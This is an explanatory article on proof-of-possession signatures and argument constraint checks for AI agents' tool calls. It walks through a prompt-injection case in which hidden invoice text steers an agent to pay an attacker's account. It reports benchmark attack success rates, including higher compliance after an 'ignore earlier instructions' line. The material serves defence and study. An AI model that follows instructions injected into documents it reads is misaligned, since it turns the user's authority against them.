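# Proof of possession and constraint checking on AI agents' tool calls

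## Agents, tool calls and borrowed authority

Proof of possession and constraint checking are security checks on the actions of AI agents. An AI agent is a language model connected to software that can act for a user, for instance by sending email, reading files or moving money. Each action begins as a *tool call*, a request by the agent to run a named function with given arguments. Proof of possession requires every call to carry a fresh signature made with the secret key to which authority for that call was granted. In constraint checking, a component in front of the tool refuses any call whose function or arguments fall outside that authority. Both checks grew out of older work on access control, but they have a new use in agents because an outsider who can get text into the model's input may be able to choose what the agent does next.

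### How text becomes an action

A language model only produces text. The *agent runtime*, an ordinary program around the model, sends the model the user's request and a description of each available tool. The runtime then parses the model's output. If the output contains a function name and arguments, the runtime runs the function with credentials it holds and adds the result to the model's input. This repeats until the model returns a final answer.

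Agents differ in how the runtime gets the tool call from the model's output. *InjecAgent* (Zhan, Liang and colleagues, 2024) tested some agents whose runtime had to find the call in free text by looking for labels such as "Action" and "Action Input", and others whose model provider returned the call already in structured form. In both designs the model proposes a call and the runtime carries it out, so the model has no contact with the payment system or the mail server.

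Suppose a user asks an agent to pay one supplier invoice. The model proposes a call that reads the file, the runtime returns the invoice's text, and the model then proposes `send_payment` with a payee, an amount and a memo. Somebody outside the user's company wrote that invoice. If it contains a hidden instruction to pay account X-99, that instruction enters the model's input alongside the user's request, and the model may act on it. This is *prompt injection*, in which an attacker places text in material an agent reads to make the model follow the attacker's instructions.

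The kind of fix that worked for similar bugs has not worked for prompt injection. In *Prompt injection is not SQL injection (it may be worse)*, a 2025 post for the UK's National Cyber Security Centre, David C compares it with SQL injection, in which a web visitor types database commands into a form. Programmers can stop SQL injection completely with parameterised queries, which mark the visitor's input as data so that the database engine never runs it. A language model has no matching boundary, because it only predicts the next token (a word or piece of a word) from all the text so far. David C thinks developers may never be able to eliminate prompt injection as they can SQL injection, so he advises them to assume that an attacker can reach every tool the model can reach. He also advises them to put most of their effort into deterministic safeguards, meaning ordinary code outside the model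 that limits what the system can do. Constraint checking is one such safeguard.

### Credentials, copies and signatures

The damage an injected instruction can do depends on the runtime's credentials. Agents commonly get one token (a string of data that a service accepts as evidence of permission) for the user's whole session. *Attenuating Authorization Tokens for Agentic Delegation Chains* (Niyikiza, 2026), a draft specification for agent credentials, describes a travel agent whose token for checking flight availability also authorises buying the flight and charging a corporate card. The invoice agent's runtime likewise attaches the session token to a payment to X-99 just as it would to the correct payment, and the bank's server finds the token valid, so the attacker does not need to forge anything or steal a password.

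Session tokens are usually *bearer tokens*, which work for anyone who has a copy. They are easy to copy in agent systems because, as Niyikiza points out, they pass through model context, tool results and messages between agents, where other components can observe them. Reusing a captured token to repeat a call is one form of *replay*.

The remedy for copying uses standard cryptography. A *key pair* is two linked numbers, a private key that its owner keeps secret and a public key that anyone may see. The owner uses the private key to compute a *signature* over a message, and anyone with the public key can check that the signature was made with the matching private key for exactly that message. The check fails if even one character of the message changes. A *hash* function reduces data of any length to a short, fixed-length digest. For a sound function such as SHA-256, nobody knows a practical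 way to find two inputs with the same digest, so a digest can identify one exact document.

An issuer can use these tools to tie a token to one party by including that party's public key in the token and signing the whole token. The party with the matching private key is the token's *holder*. If a service requires a fresh signature from the holder on every call, a copy of the token alone is not enough to make a call. The signature shows which key signed a call, but not why the call was made. If the invoice agent's runtime signs whatever the model proposes, it will put a valid signature on the payment to X-99.

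### The confused deputy

Norm Hardy's *The Confused Deputy* (1988) describes much the same failure in a program with no AI, in a story he calls nearly true. In the late 1970s, Tymshare, a company that sold time on shared computers, had a compiler that recorded usage statistics in a file in its directory, SYSX. The staff therefore gave the compiler permission to write to files in SYSX. The compiler also let users name a file to receive debugging output, and one user named the billing file, which was also in SYSX. The compiler passed the name to the operating system, which allowed the write because the compiler had permission, and Tymshare lost its billing information.

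Hardy considers the obvious fixes and finds that none of them works. The compiler could not reject names in other directories, because users had good reasons to send output there. Rejecting everything in SYSX would have blocked people with legitimate access to that directory, and a list of sensitive files would have needed updating whenever somebody added one. Tymshare added a system call that let the compiler choose between its own licence and the user's. But some applications soon needed more than two sources of authority, and by then the rules for opening a file had grown to fourteen logical operators.

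In his diagnosis, the compiler held authority from two sources and could not keep them apart. The file's name and the permission to write to it also arrived separately. A *confused deputy* is a program that has its own authority and is induced to use it for someone who lacks that authority. The invoice agent fits this description closely because the invoice supplies the payee's name and the session token supplies the permission to pay.

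Hardy's answer was to combine name and permission in a single thing, called a *capability*. According to the history *Early Capability Architectures*, Dennis and Van Horn of MIT had introduced the term in 1966 in a design for a hypothetical operating system. Each running program in their design has a list of capabilities, each identifying one object, such as a segment of memory, and the kinds of access allowed. A program refers to an object by giving the position of an entry in its list, so it cannot refer to an object without using a permission for it. It can start a subordinate program with an empty list and copy into that list only capabilities from its own. Under such a system, Tymshare's user would have given the compiler a capability for an output file instead of a typed name. A user with no capability for the billing file could not have given the compiler one.

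Programs must not be able to forge capabilities. The first machine to use capabilities, a PDP-1 minicomputer at MIT, kept each program's list of them in memory that only the operating system could change. An agent and a bank share no operating system, so a signature has to prevent forgery instead. A *capability token* is a signed credential that lists which tools its holder may call and with what arguments. Before a tool runs, an *enforcement point* compares the call with the token and permits or refuses it.

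Hardy's compiler is an imperfect analogy for a language model. Given two capabilities, the compiler's programmers could write code that always used one for statistics and the other for debugging output. Nobody can build the same guarantee into a language model, which is why David C calls such models "inherently confusable" deputies. Capabilities don't make the model harder to mislead, but they limit what it can do when misled. Niyikiza accepts that an attacker can still steer an agent among the resources its token covers, so he advises issuers to make the token presented for a call as narrow as the task permits.

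### A draft specification and an invoice

Niyikiza's draft develops the capability idea in detail for agents by defining Attenuating Authorization Tokens (AATs). A trusted issuer signs a *root token*, which sets the upper limit of authority for all tokens derived from it. A holder can then make a *derived token* for another agent without contacting the issuer, if the new token's authority is equal to or narrower than its parent's. This narrowing is called *attenuation*. An enforcement point that knows the issuer's public key can check the whole chain of tokens without a network connection to the issuer.

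The document is an Internet-Draft, a working text submitted to the Internet Engineering Task Force (IETF), which develops many of the internet's technical standards. It has no standing as a standard. Its header names the group that maintains OAuth, a widely used framework for issuing access tokens, and lists the intended status as "Standards Track", but those entries reflect only the author's aim. The IETF's tracker lists Niyikiza's text as an individual draft that belongs to no publication stream. As of October 2026, the latest version was revision 01, dated 15 June 2026, which expires on 17 December 2026.

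The design is still changing. In Niyikiza's first version, from March 2026, tokens for delegating and tokens for calling tools were separate types, and one example used a text pattern to limit file paths. The June revision has a single token type and no pattern rule in its core vocabulary. Another Internet-Draft, *Agent Delegation Chain* (2026), takes a similar approach and states a plan to converge with Niyikiza's. On the OAuth mailing list, a correspondent named Neil questioned the design, noting that a parent token remains valid after its holder derives a child token from it. He asked what would stop an agent from replaying a parent token to the agents above it.

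Most of the evidence that the scheme works as intended comes from Tenuo, the company that makes the reference implementation and where Niyikiza works. Niyikiza reports that formal verification of the attenuation rules is unfinished. An automated search for counterexamples, limited to 8 constraints and 8 values, has found none. This gives some reassurance about the logic of the rules but does not show whether any particular deployment applies them correctly.

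In the draft's notation, the invoice case looks like this. The user's *orchestrating agent*, which plans the work and may pass parts of it to other agents, holds a root token valid for one hour. The token contains the agent's public key and this grant:

```json
"send_payment": {
  "payee":  { "constraint_type": "one_of",
              "values": ["A-17", "A-22"] },
  "amount": { "constraint_type": "range",
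              "min": 0, "min_inclusive": false, "max": 500 },
  "memo":   { "constraint_type": "wildcard" }
}
```

Each entry is a *constraint*, a rule that an argument's value must satisfy before the tool runs. The agent may pay supplier A-17 or A-22, in an amount above 0 and up to 500, with any text as the memo. An enforcement point that applies these rules will refuse the payment to X-99 even if the hidden text persuades the agent to request it. The grant is still wider than the task, because the user wanted one invoice paid and the token covers two suppliers.

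### Four attackers

The protection that a token gives depends on what the attacker controls, and four cases need separate treatment.

A thief who copies an agent's bearer token, perhaps from a log file or a message between agents, can do everything the agent could do. If the token is tied to a key, the thief can do very little with it, because the private key never left the runtime.

A *hijacked model* is one whose proposed calls an attacker steers without compromising the runtime or its keys. Such an attacker, like the one who hid text in the invoice, needs no access to the user's machine and never sees the key, because the runtime signs on the model's behalf.

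With a *compromised runtime*, the attacker runs code inside the agent program and can use or copy the signing key. The attacker can then write and sign calls without going through the model. If the agent has a tool that executes arbitrary code, hijacking the model may be enough to take over the runtime.

With a *compromised sub-agent*, the attacker controls an agent further down the chain, such as a specialised payment agent to which the orchestrating agent passes the payment. The payment agent has its own key and derived token. The attacker can use that token, but attenuation is meant to prevent them from using it to gain the orchestrator's wider authority.

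### Measuring hijacked models

Researchers use benchmarks to measure how vulnerable agents are to prompt injection. A benchmark is a fixed collection of tasks and attacks that anyone can run against an agent. The usual metric is the *attack success rate*, the share of attacks in which the agent carried out the attacker's action.

*AgentDojo* (Debenedetti, Zhang and colleagues, 2024) simulates four settings: an office workspace, the messaging service Slack, a travel agency and a bank. It has 97 user tasks and 27 attacker goals, and pairs every task with every goal in the same setting, for a total of 629 security cases. In one banking task, the user asks the agent to pay a bill stored in a file, and one of the paired attacker goals is to send as much money as possible to the attacker's account. The agent calls tools that change the simulated accounts and mailboxes, and ordinary code then inspects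 the result. The team did not use a second language model as judge because an injection that fooled the agent might also fool the judge.

They also count how many user tasks the agent completes, with and without an attack. An agent that refuses every call has an attack success rate of zero but is useless. Weaker models also often looked safer in their tests because they failed to complete the attacker's task even after the injection had worked on them.

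InjecAgent, by Zhan and colleagues, is a simpler test that combines 17 user requests with 62 attacker instructions, for 1,054 cases. Thirty of the instructions would cause direct harm, such as transferring money or unlocking a front door. The other 32 aim to steal data, and those attacks count as successful only if the agent both fetches the data and sends it out. The model receives a tool result that already contains the injection, and the researchers check which call it produces next. Their main figure excludes garbled outputs.

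AgentDojo and InjecAgent score attacks blocked at the tool boundary differently. AgentDojo's code inspects the state of the bank afterwards, so a payment that an enforcement point blocks counts as a failed attack. InjecAgent scores the model's output, so the same payment counts as a successful attack unless the experimenters apply the check before scoring. Neither benchmark was designed to test stolen tokens or copied keys, so a low attack success rate on either is evidence only about hijacked models.

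The original scores are now out of date. In 2024 the InjecAgent team found that GPT-4, prompted to use tools, gave in to 24% of attacks, and to 47% when a stock line telling it to ignore earlier instructions came first. AgentDojo's original attacks succeeded in fewer than 25% of cases against the best-performing agents. AgentDojo is still in use and has grown to more than 900 combinations of task and attack, according to *Assessing Automated Prompt Injection Attacks in Agentic Environments* (2026). *The Surface You Test Is Not the Surface That Breaks* (2026) used it to test 13 models from six providers.

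*StepGuard* (2026) uses AgentDojo and AgentDyn, a newer benchmark with longer and more open-ended tasks. AgentDyn includes helpful instructions from third parties that an agent has to follow to finish its work. An honest invoice, for example, contains instructions of this kind, including whom to pay.

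## Proof of possession: signing each tool call

The orchestrating agent in the invoice example holds a root token that permits payments of up to 500 to A-17 or A-22. Proof of possession makes a stolen copy of that token useless on its own. Niyikiza's draft describes the procedure in enough detail to follow one payment from start to finish.

### One signed payment

The runtime first needs a token with its key in it. It generates a key pair and sends the public key to the issuer with its request for a root token. Niyikiza advises the issuer to demand evidence that the runtime also has the private key, such as a signed statement. The issuer then puts the public key in the token's `cnf` field. The name is short for "confirmation", and the IETF standard RFC 7800 defines the field for this purpose:

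```json
"cnf": {
  "jwk": { "kty": "OKP", "crv": "Ed25519",
           "x": "11qYAYKxCrfVS_7TyWQHOg7hcvPapiMlrwIaaPcHURo" }
}
```

The string after `x` is the public key. Ed25519 is a common signature scheme that every implementation of the draft must support. The issuer signs the whole token, including the `cnf` field, so a thief who swaps in a different key invalidates the token.

Suppose the model now reads an honest invoice and proposes paying 240 to A-17. The runtime writes a short JSON document about this one call:

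```json
{
  "jti": "proof-7f3a91",
  "iat": 1791367200,
  "aat_id": "root-5521",
  "aat_tool": "send_payment",
  "aat_aud": "https://pay.example.com",
  "hta": { "payee": "A-17", "amount": 240, "memo": "Invoice 1043" }
}
```

The `jti` field is a random identifier that the runtime must never use twice (real ones are longer than the one shown). `iat` is the time in seconds since the start of 1970, here 10:00 UTC on 7 October 2026. `aat_id` repeats the token's identifier, and `aat_tool` and `hta` give the function and its arguments. The optional `aat_aud` names the service that should accept the proof.

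A signature covers exact bytes, and two programs can write the same JSON differently. One might put `amount` before `payee`, add spaces or write 240.0 for 240. The signature would then fail even though nobody had tampered with the call. RFC 8785 solves this with a canonical form, which sorts the field names, drops optional spaces and allows only one spelling of each number and string. The payment then becomes a single line:

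```
{"aat_aud":"https://pay.example.com","aat_id":"root-5521","aat_tool":"send_payment","hta":{"amount":240,"memo":"Invoice 1043","payee":"A-17"},"iat":1791367200,"jti":"proof-7f3a91"}
```

The runtime encodes this line, and a short header naming the signature algorithm, in base64url, a way of writing any bytes with characters that are safe in web addresses. It joins the two parts with a full stop and signs the result:

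```
signing_input = base64url(header) + "." + base64url(canonical payload)
signature     = sign(private key, signing_input)
```

The header, payload and signature form a JSON Web Token (JWT), the format the draft also uses for root and derived tokens. The runtime sends this proof to the enforcement point along with the root token and the call.

The enforcement point starts with the root token. It verifies the issuer's signature and the expiry time, and compares the arguments with the grant. It looks at the proof only after that, because anyone can make up a token containing their own key and sign a flawless proof for it. The proof must then meet seven conditions:

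1. The algorithm in the header is on the enforcement point's own list and suits the type of key in `cnf`.
2. The signature verifies with that key.
3. `aat_id` equals the identifier of the token.
4. `aat_aud` names this service, if the deployment requires an audience.
5. `aat_tool` matches the requested function exactly, character for character.
6. `hta` equals the arguments of the call, with both in canonical form.
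7. `iat` is close enough to the current time.

The rule about algorithms prevents an old vulnerability in JWT software. Some programs accepted unsigned tokens whose header gave the algorithm as "none".

Comparing the arguments makes this a proof about the tool call and not just the web request. The enforcement point takes the arguments from the call it received, puts them into canonical form itself and compares the bytes with the signed version. Suppose a proxy between the runtime and the bank changes the payee to A-22 and the amount to 500. The grant allows both values, so constraint checking alone would let the altered payment through. But the altered arguments don't match the signed ones, and the proxy cannot correct `hta` without the private key.

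RFC 8785 treats every number as a double-precision floating-point value, a format that cannot represent every whole number above 2^53 (about nine quadrillion). If a tool takes a 17-digit account number as a number, the last digit may change, and two different accounts may have the same canonical form. Passing account numbers as text avoids the problem.

### Signing the request or signing the call

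OAuth already has a standard for signed requests, called DPoP (Demonstrating Proof of Possession, RFC 9449). The client signs a small JWT for each request, and its access token is tied to the key it signs with. The JWT contains the HTTP method (such as GET or POST), the web address without its query string, the time, a random identifier and a hash of the access token. It doesn't cover the request's body or other headers.

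That works reasonably well for a service with a separate address for each operation, since `POST /refunds` reveals much of what the request will do. Many agents, though, reach their tools through the Model Context Protocol (MCP), which Anthropic introduced in November 2024. An MCP client in the agent's software sends requests to an MCP server, which offers the tools. *Breaking the Protocol* (Maloyan and Namiot, 2026) reports that over 5,000 community-built servers appeared within months of the release. All tool calls to one server go to the same address, and the tool's name and arguments are in the request's body.

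The DPoP proofs for reading a file and for sending money through the same MCP server therefore contain the same method and address. A proxy that can rewrite the request body could turn the file read into a money transfer, and the signature would still verify.

Mutual TLS works at the level of the connection. TLS is the encryption behind `https`, and normally only the server proves its identity with a certificate. In mutual TLS, the client also presents a certificate and proves that it has the matching private key when it opens the connection. RFC 8705 lets an issuer put a hash of the client's certificate in the access token. The server then accepts the token only over a connection that the client opened with that certificate.

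TLS protects everything sent over a connection, including the request body, but only until it reaches the machine that decrypts it. Large services often decrypt traffic at a gateway and forward it internally. Any component behind the gateway can then change the payee, and the call has no signature that would reveal the change. Mutual TLS also leaves no signed record of each call for an investigator to check later.

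Niyikiza's proof passes through gateways and other agents unchanged because the signature is tied to the call, not the connection. However, the proof does not cover HTTP headers, so if a payment service used a header to choose which account to debit, a proxy could switch accounts without changing the signed arguments. The draft also does not specify how to send the token and proof over HTTP. The mechanisms can be combined, for instance by sending a tool-call proof over a connection protected by mutual TLS.

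| Mechanism | What the proof covers | What someone could still alter |
|---|---|---|
| DPoP | HTTP method, address, time and token | Function name, arguments and the rest of the body; other headers |
| Mutual TLS | Everything on the connection | The whole request, once a gateway has decrypted it |
| Tool-call proof | Function name, arguments, time, token and, if required, audience | HTTP headers and anything else outside the arguments |

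### Sending the same proof twice

A thief who captures both the token and the proof cannot change the payment but can resubmit it until the proof's timestamp is too old. Niyikiza recommends accepting proofs stamped within 30 seconds of the time on the enforcement point's clock, since the runtime's clock may be slow or fast.

For the proof stamped 10:00:00, the window runs from 09:59:30 to 10:00:30, or 60 seconds in all. If both clocks are right, the thief has 30 seconds from the moment of signing. If the runtime's clock is 30 seconds fast, the runtime actually signs at 09:59:30 and the thief has the full minute. The draft suggests a tolerance of 5 to 10 seconds for cloud deployments, because cloud providers keep their clocks closely synchronised. It advises against any tolerance above 60 seconds.

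Even in ten seconds, a program can submit a payment hundreds of times. For calls with side effects, the draft therefore requires the enforcement point to record the `jti` of every proof it accepts and refuse any proof that repeats one. It can delete an identifier once the proof is too old to pass the time check. A service handling 1,000 calls a second would need to store at most about 60,000 identifiers. The enforcement point must look up and record each identifier in one indivisible step, or two copies of a proof that arrive together might both pass.

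The draft also has a simpler option that needs no record. The enforcement point divides time into 30-second blocks and accepts proofs from the current block and the one before. A thief who captures a proof early in a block can use it until the end of the next block, so the draft forbids this method for calls with side effects. The method suits calls such as reading a file, where repetition does no damage.

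Recording identifiers may not stop a replay when there is more than one enforcement point. Suppose the payment service has one in Frankfurt and one in Dublin, each with its own list. A thief could capture a proof that Frankfurt has already accepted and submit it in Dublin, where its identifier is not on the list. If the `aat_aud` field names the Frankfurt address, Dublin refuses the proof. Niyikiza recommends requiring the field wherever several enforcement points would accept the same token.

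Servers behind a single address also share an audience, so they need a common list, kept in a shared database. The draft's main convenience is that an enforcement point can verify a token without contacting anyone, and the shared list takes away part of that. For a payment, the enforcement point now has to reach the database. If the database is down, the enforcement point must either refuse the payment or risk making it twice. The draft leaves the design of the database to each deployment.

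A related problem can occur without an attacker. If the connection drops after the runtime sends the payment, the runtime cannot determine whether the bank carried it out. Resending the old proof will fail, but a newly signed proof will pass because it has a new identifier, and the supplier may be paid twice. The usual remedy is for the payment service to take a reference, such as the invoice number, and make only one payment for each reference. Niyikiza recommends safeguards of this kind for high-value operations.

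### The four attackers

A thief who has only a copy of the token cannot sign a proof, so the enforcement point refuses every call the thief makes. The draft does not encrypt tokens, however, so the copy may still reveal useful information. Anyone who sees the invoice agent's token, for example, learns which suppliers the company pays through that agent, and up to what amount.

The same protection partly addresses the question Neil raised on the OAuth mailing list about replaying a parent token. When the orchestrating agent passes authority to a payment agent, the payment agent must present the orchestrator's token with its own, so it always has a copy of the parent token. It cannot make calls with that copy alone, because those calls would need a signature from the orchestrator's key.

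The runtime signs a hijacked model's tool calls, so the model does not need to steal anything. The injected payment to X-99 arrives with a proof that meets all seven conditions, and the enforcement point refuses it only because the grant does not list X-99. If the hidden text instead specifies a payment of 500 to A-22, the enforcement point allows it. The signature then provides only a record linking the payment to the agent's key.

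The grant also limits an attacker who has compromised the runtime. They cannot pay X-99 or send more than 500 at once, but within those restrictions they can make calls without getting the model to make them.

An attacker who controls the payment agent cannot sign as the orchestrator, because the payment agent's key works only with tokens that name it.

### Keeping the key safe

Whether an attacker who compromises the runtime can steal the key depends on where it is stored. In the simplest design, the key is in the runtime's memory or in a file, and any code running in the runtime can copy it. The attacker can then keep signing tool calls from another machine after the defenders have cleaned up the first.

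A safer design keeps the key in a separate signing process. The runtime sends this process a payload and gets back a signature, but can't read the key. An attacker in the runtime can still request signatures, but only while they have access. A hardware key store, such as the security chip in a laptop or a dedicated module in a data centre, offers the same protection even if the attacker controls the operating system. Many of these devices support the P-256 elliptic curve but not Ed25519, so a deployment may have to use ES256, which uses P-256 and is on the draft's recommended list.

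Neither arrangement helps against a hijacked model, since the requests for signatures come from a runtime that is working normally.

Niyikiza also recommends separate keys for agents that plan and agents that call tools. In the invoice case, the orchestrating agent would have one key and the payment agent another, and the orchestrator would derive a token naming the payment agent's key. Someone who steals the payment agent's key then gets only that agent's authority, and investigators can tell which of the two agents signed a call. The separation protects less if someone steals the orchestrator's key. An agent can pass on payment authority only if its own token includes it, and the draft lets any holder present its own token to a tool. The attacker could therefore skip the payment agent and pay suppliers directly. Enforcement points do not check an agent's role unless a deployment adds rules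 for this.

A thief with both the root token and its key can use the full grant until the token expires. In the example, the thief could make any number of payments of up to 500 each to either supplier for up to an hour. The thief can also derive new tokens for other keys, but none can last longer than the root token or permit more. The draft has no procedure for cancelling a token early. Niyikiza accepts this limitation so that enforcement points can verify tokens offline, and his main advice is to keep lifetimes short.

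Token expiry stops an attacker only if they cannot get a new token. The runtime logs in to the issuer with a credential that the draft treats as separate from the signing key. If both are on the same compromised machine, the attacker can steal them and request a new root token every hour until someone revokes the login credential.

### Tying credentials to the agent's code

Several agents often run inside one program and share its OAuth identity. A service then cannot tell an agent that should only read settings from one that may change them. In *Agentic JWT*, Goswami (2025) tries to solve this by giving each agent its own identity and signing key, even when they share a process.

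A small library, which Goswami calls a shim, runs alongside the agents. It hashes an agent's prompt, tools and configuration, and uses the resulting checksum to authenticate the agent to the authorisation server, where the agent has a registered identity. The shim tracks which step of an approved workflow the agent has reached and obtains a token for that step. It then derives a key specific to that agent, attaches the signed proof and sends the request.

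This gives a service information that an ordinary key cannot. If someone adds a tool to the payment agent or rewrites its standing instructions, the checksum changes and the agent can no longer authenticate. The workflow also rules out some injected calls. For example, an approved workflow that reads an invoice and then pays it has no step for exporting the customer list, so a hijacked model could not get a token for the export.

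However, hidden text in an invoice does not change the checksum. The authorisation server must know the correct checksum in advance, so it cannot cover documents that the agent will read later. A payment to the wrong supplier does not break the workflow either, because the workflow expects a payment at that point. The design catches changes to the agent's code and sequence of actions, but catching a change of payee requires a constraint on the call's payee argument.

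The design also depends on the shim being trustworthy. Goswami describes it as tamper-proof, but it runs in the same process as the agents it identifies, so an attacker who can run code there may be able to read its keys or make it report the expected checksum. The shim also sends a checksum of itself, but a modified shim could send the old value. Goswami proposes, as an option, a trusted execution environment, which is an isolated part of a processor whose hardware can certify which code is running inside it. This would make a false report much harder, but it requires suitable hardware.

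The evidence so far comes from a prototype, which blocked every attack Goswami tried on a small multi-agent service. However, he chose those attacks himself and left a full evaluation to a later article. He has since submitted the design to the IETF as an Internet-Draft, *Secure Intent Protocol* (Goswami, 2026), dated 27 June 2026. Its intended status is "Informational", so it is not meant to become a standard.

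### Authenticating the server

DPoP, Niyikiza's draft and Agentic JWT all have the caller sign. Maloyan and Namiot deal with messages from the server, since a malicious MCP server can send instructions to the model. They found that MCP's first version had no authentication or replay protection for individual messages and relied on TLS alone. Their proposed extension, AttestMCP, gives each server a certificate listing what it may do. The server adds its identity, a timestamp, a random value and an HMAC to its messages.

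An HMAC is a hash computed with a secret key that both sides share. It is fast and shows that nobody outside the pair altered the message. But anyone who can check an HMAC can also create one, so it cannot prove to a third party which side wrote the message. Niyikiza similarly excludes shared-key methods from the algorithms permitted for tokens because they cannot tie a token to one holder.

To block replayed messages, AttestMCP stores the last 1,000 random values from each server and rejects messages more than 30 seconds old. A server that sends more than about 33 messages a second would fill that list in under 30 seconds. If the client then drops the oldest values, an attacker could replay the messages that contained them while those messages are still less than 30 seconds old.

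Maloyan and Namiot ran 847 attack scenarios against agents based on Claude 3.5 Sonnet, GPT-4o and Llama 3.1 70B, all now several generations old. AttestMCP reduced the overall attack success rate from 52.8% to 12.4%. It added a median of 8.3 milliseconds to a message when the client had not yet stored the server's certificate.

It would be a mistake to credit the HMAC with most of that fall. In attacks through the content of retrieved documents, the success rate dropped from 47.8% to 18.4%, yet an honest server would put a perfectly valid HMAC on a poisoned document. AttestMCP also labels where some messages come from and asks the user before data from one server reaches another. That second measure had a large effect in a separate comparison of attacks that spread between servers:

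| Flow of data between servers | Attack success rate | Tasks completed |
|---|---|---|
| Unrestricted | 61.3% | 94.2% |
| After asking the user | 31.7% | 87.4% |
| Forbidden | 8.7% | 61.8% |

The AttestMCP paper describes asking the user about transfers between servers as the default setting, but the 8.7% success rate it gives elsewhere for attacks between servers is the figure for forbidding those transfers. Forbidding them also reduces task completion to 61.8%, so a reader who cites the 8.7% as AttestMCP's benefit should include that drop.

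Maloyan's doctoral thesis, *Evaluating and Improving the Robustness of Large Language Models* (2026), also describes AttestMCP, with somewhat different numbers. It reports that the attack success rate fell from 53.7% to 12.4% over 847 scenarios, with an overhead of less than 0.1 milliseconds per call. The 12.4% figure is for a group of defences that includes both AttestMCP and running the agent's code in isolation. In the thesis, AttestMCP itself consists of the HMAC and a table of the calls allowed in a session. The earlier paper measured 0.3 milliseconds for the HMAC alone, so the timings are not directly comparable.

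### What MCP requires now

MCP launched without any rules on authorisation. *MCP has tightened its authentication rules four times* (Dhamsania, 2026) describes the revisions that followed. One in March 2025 added a framework based on OAuth 2.1, and one in June 2025 required clients requesting a token to state which server it was for. Revisions in November 2025 and July 2026 changed how clients register with an authorisation server. Dhamsania warns that servers built in the first year may still rely on assumptions that the protocol has since dropped.

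The current rules are in Model Context Protocol's *Authorization* (2026), part of the 28 July 2026 revision. Authorisation is still optional, and servers that communicate with the client as local processes should get their credentials by other means. When a web server uses authorisation, the client must name that server whenever it requests a token. The server must reject any token not meant for it and must not forward the client's token to another service.

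These rules bind the token to an audience. A thief who copies the payment server's token cannot use it at the mail server, but can still use it at the payment server because the rules don't tie the token to the client that received it. Tying it to the client would take proof of possession, which the July revision does not require. Clients must send their token in a header that begins `Authorization: Bearer`, and the specification's list of underlying standards includes neither DPoP nor mutual TLS.

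A deployment could add mutual TLS without breaking the header rule, because RFC 8705 leaves the header unchanged. DPoP replaces the word `Bearer` with `DPoP`, so using it would depart from the specification's text.

To limit the risk from stolen tokens, Model Context Protocol's *Authorization Security Considerations* (2026) requires clients and servers to store tokens securely and recommends short token lifetimes. It also requires clients to use PKCE, a proof made when the client obtains its token. The client sends the authorisation server a hash of a secret, receives a temporary code through the user's browser, and must reveal the secret to exchange the code for a token. A thief who intercepts the code cannot redeem it without the secret, but PKCE does not protect the token after it is issued.

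Model Context Protocol (MCP) tokens also describe authority less precisely than the grant in the invoice example. The specification uses *scopes*, which are labels such as `files:read` or `files:write`, and does not define limits on individual arguments. When a task needs more authority, under the specification the client should request a new token that covers both the scopes it requested before and the new ones. This saves the user from repeating approvals, but a token copied late in a long session is likely to permit more actions than a token copied at the start.

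The Agentic AI Foundation's *Authorization in MCP 2026-07-28* reviews the six authorisation changes in the July revision and concludes that they clarify existing OAuth practice without adding new concepts. The name of one change, "credential binding", could mislead. It means that a client may not use credentials it received from one authorisation server with another. It does not put the client's key in the access token.

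### The discussion at the IETF

Some companies already go further than MCP requires. *AI Identity* (2026) reports that Block, a payments company, uses OAuth with WIMSE in production. WIMSE is a set of IETF specifications for identifying running programs to one another. Its proof tokens contain a fresh signature over the HTTP method, the address, the time and a random value. Like DPoP proofs, they protect against the use of a stolen token, but the signature does not cover the arguments of a tool call.

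The OAuth working group is considering a proof-of-possession format that could cover the contents of a tool call. In September 2026 it held a series of online meetings on whether OAuth's older assumptions still suit software agents, with more planned for October. *OAuth Is Asking What Authorization Needs to Become* (Flanagan, 2026) describes the meeting of 14 September, which discussed a proposal to prove possession with HTTP Message Signatures. In this existing standard, the sender chooses which parts of a web request to sign and can include a digest of the body. For an MCP request, the body contains the function name and arguments. Signing the digest would therefore stop a proxy from turning a file read into a payment, which DPoP does not prevent.

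The proposal's benefit to agents depends on whether it requires the digest, because a sender who omits it gets roughly the same protection as with DPoP. Flanagan also cautions that discussion in the working group does not mean the proposal has been accepted as a standard.

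## Checking arguments against explicit constraints

A valid signature on a payment shows which key made the request, but not whether the company owes the payee any money. Compare these two calls:

```
send_payment(payee="A-17", amount=240, memo="Invoice 1043")
send_payment(payee="X-99", amount=240, memo="Invoice 1043")
```

The first call pays a supplier and the second pays a thief. A permission that covers the whole function, such as an OAuth scope called `payments:write`, allows both calls. Taking `send_payment` away from the agent would stop the theft, but it would also stop the agent from paying invoices.

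Checking types doesn't help either. Agent software often checks each call against a *schema*, which lists a function's arguments and their types, but "A-17" and "X-99" both pass because both are text. Distinguishing the two calls requires checking the payee's value.

### What agent frameworks check by default

Most developers build agents on a framework that parses the model's output and runs the tools. *Capability Gates Are Not Authorization* (Mellafe Zuvic, 2026) examines the public source code of three products to find out whether common frameworks check argument values. The paper uses *capability gating* for deciding which tools an agent has, and *per-call authorization* for deciding whether the agent may make a particular call with particular argument values. All three products had capability gating, but by default none of them checked the values against a policy before running the tool.

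LangChain and its companion LangGraph look up the tool's name in a table, usually check the arguments' types, and run the function. Developers can attach code that observes each call, but this code can't be relied on to block one. They can also add a step for a person to approve calls. LlamaIndex works similarly. If the model names a tool that doesn't exist, LlamaIndex returns an error to the model and does not treat the request as a security event.

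The Stripe Agent Toolkit, which connects agents to the payment company Stripe, has a fixed list of permitted actions and uses an API key whose permissions the merchant can restrict. Within those limits, it forwards whatever amount, currency and customer the model supplies. Mellafe Zuvic did not examine Stripe's own servers, which may make further checks. He doesn't call the missing check a vulnerability in any of the three products, because their documented designs leave it to the developer.

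To demonstrate the gap, he built a LangChain tool that changes which account receives a simulated merchant's money. He replaced the model with a fixed output requesting the account `acct_ATTACKER_999`, so that anyone could reproduce the result. LangChain ran the call and changed the account. He then sent the same call through ScopeGate, a check he had written, which refused it because the policy listed only `acct_MERCHANT_001`.

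A missing check matters only if models attempt unauthorised calls. In a companion benchmark of 27 models, Mellafe Zuvic used injections that presented the dangerous action as a necessary part of the user's task. On average, the 12 cheaper models attempted the unauthorised call in 60.3% of trials and the 15 flagship models in 18.9%. Gemini 3.1 Pro Preview never attempted it, while GPT-4o mini always did. Wording made a large difference. GLM-4.7 followed 28.3% of crude injections but all of those framed as part of the task. The figures are for attempts in a sandbox, and one author wrote all the scenarios.

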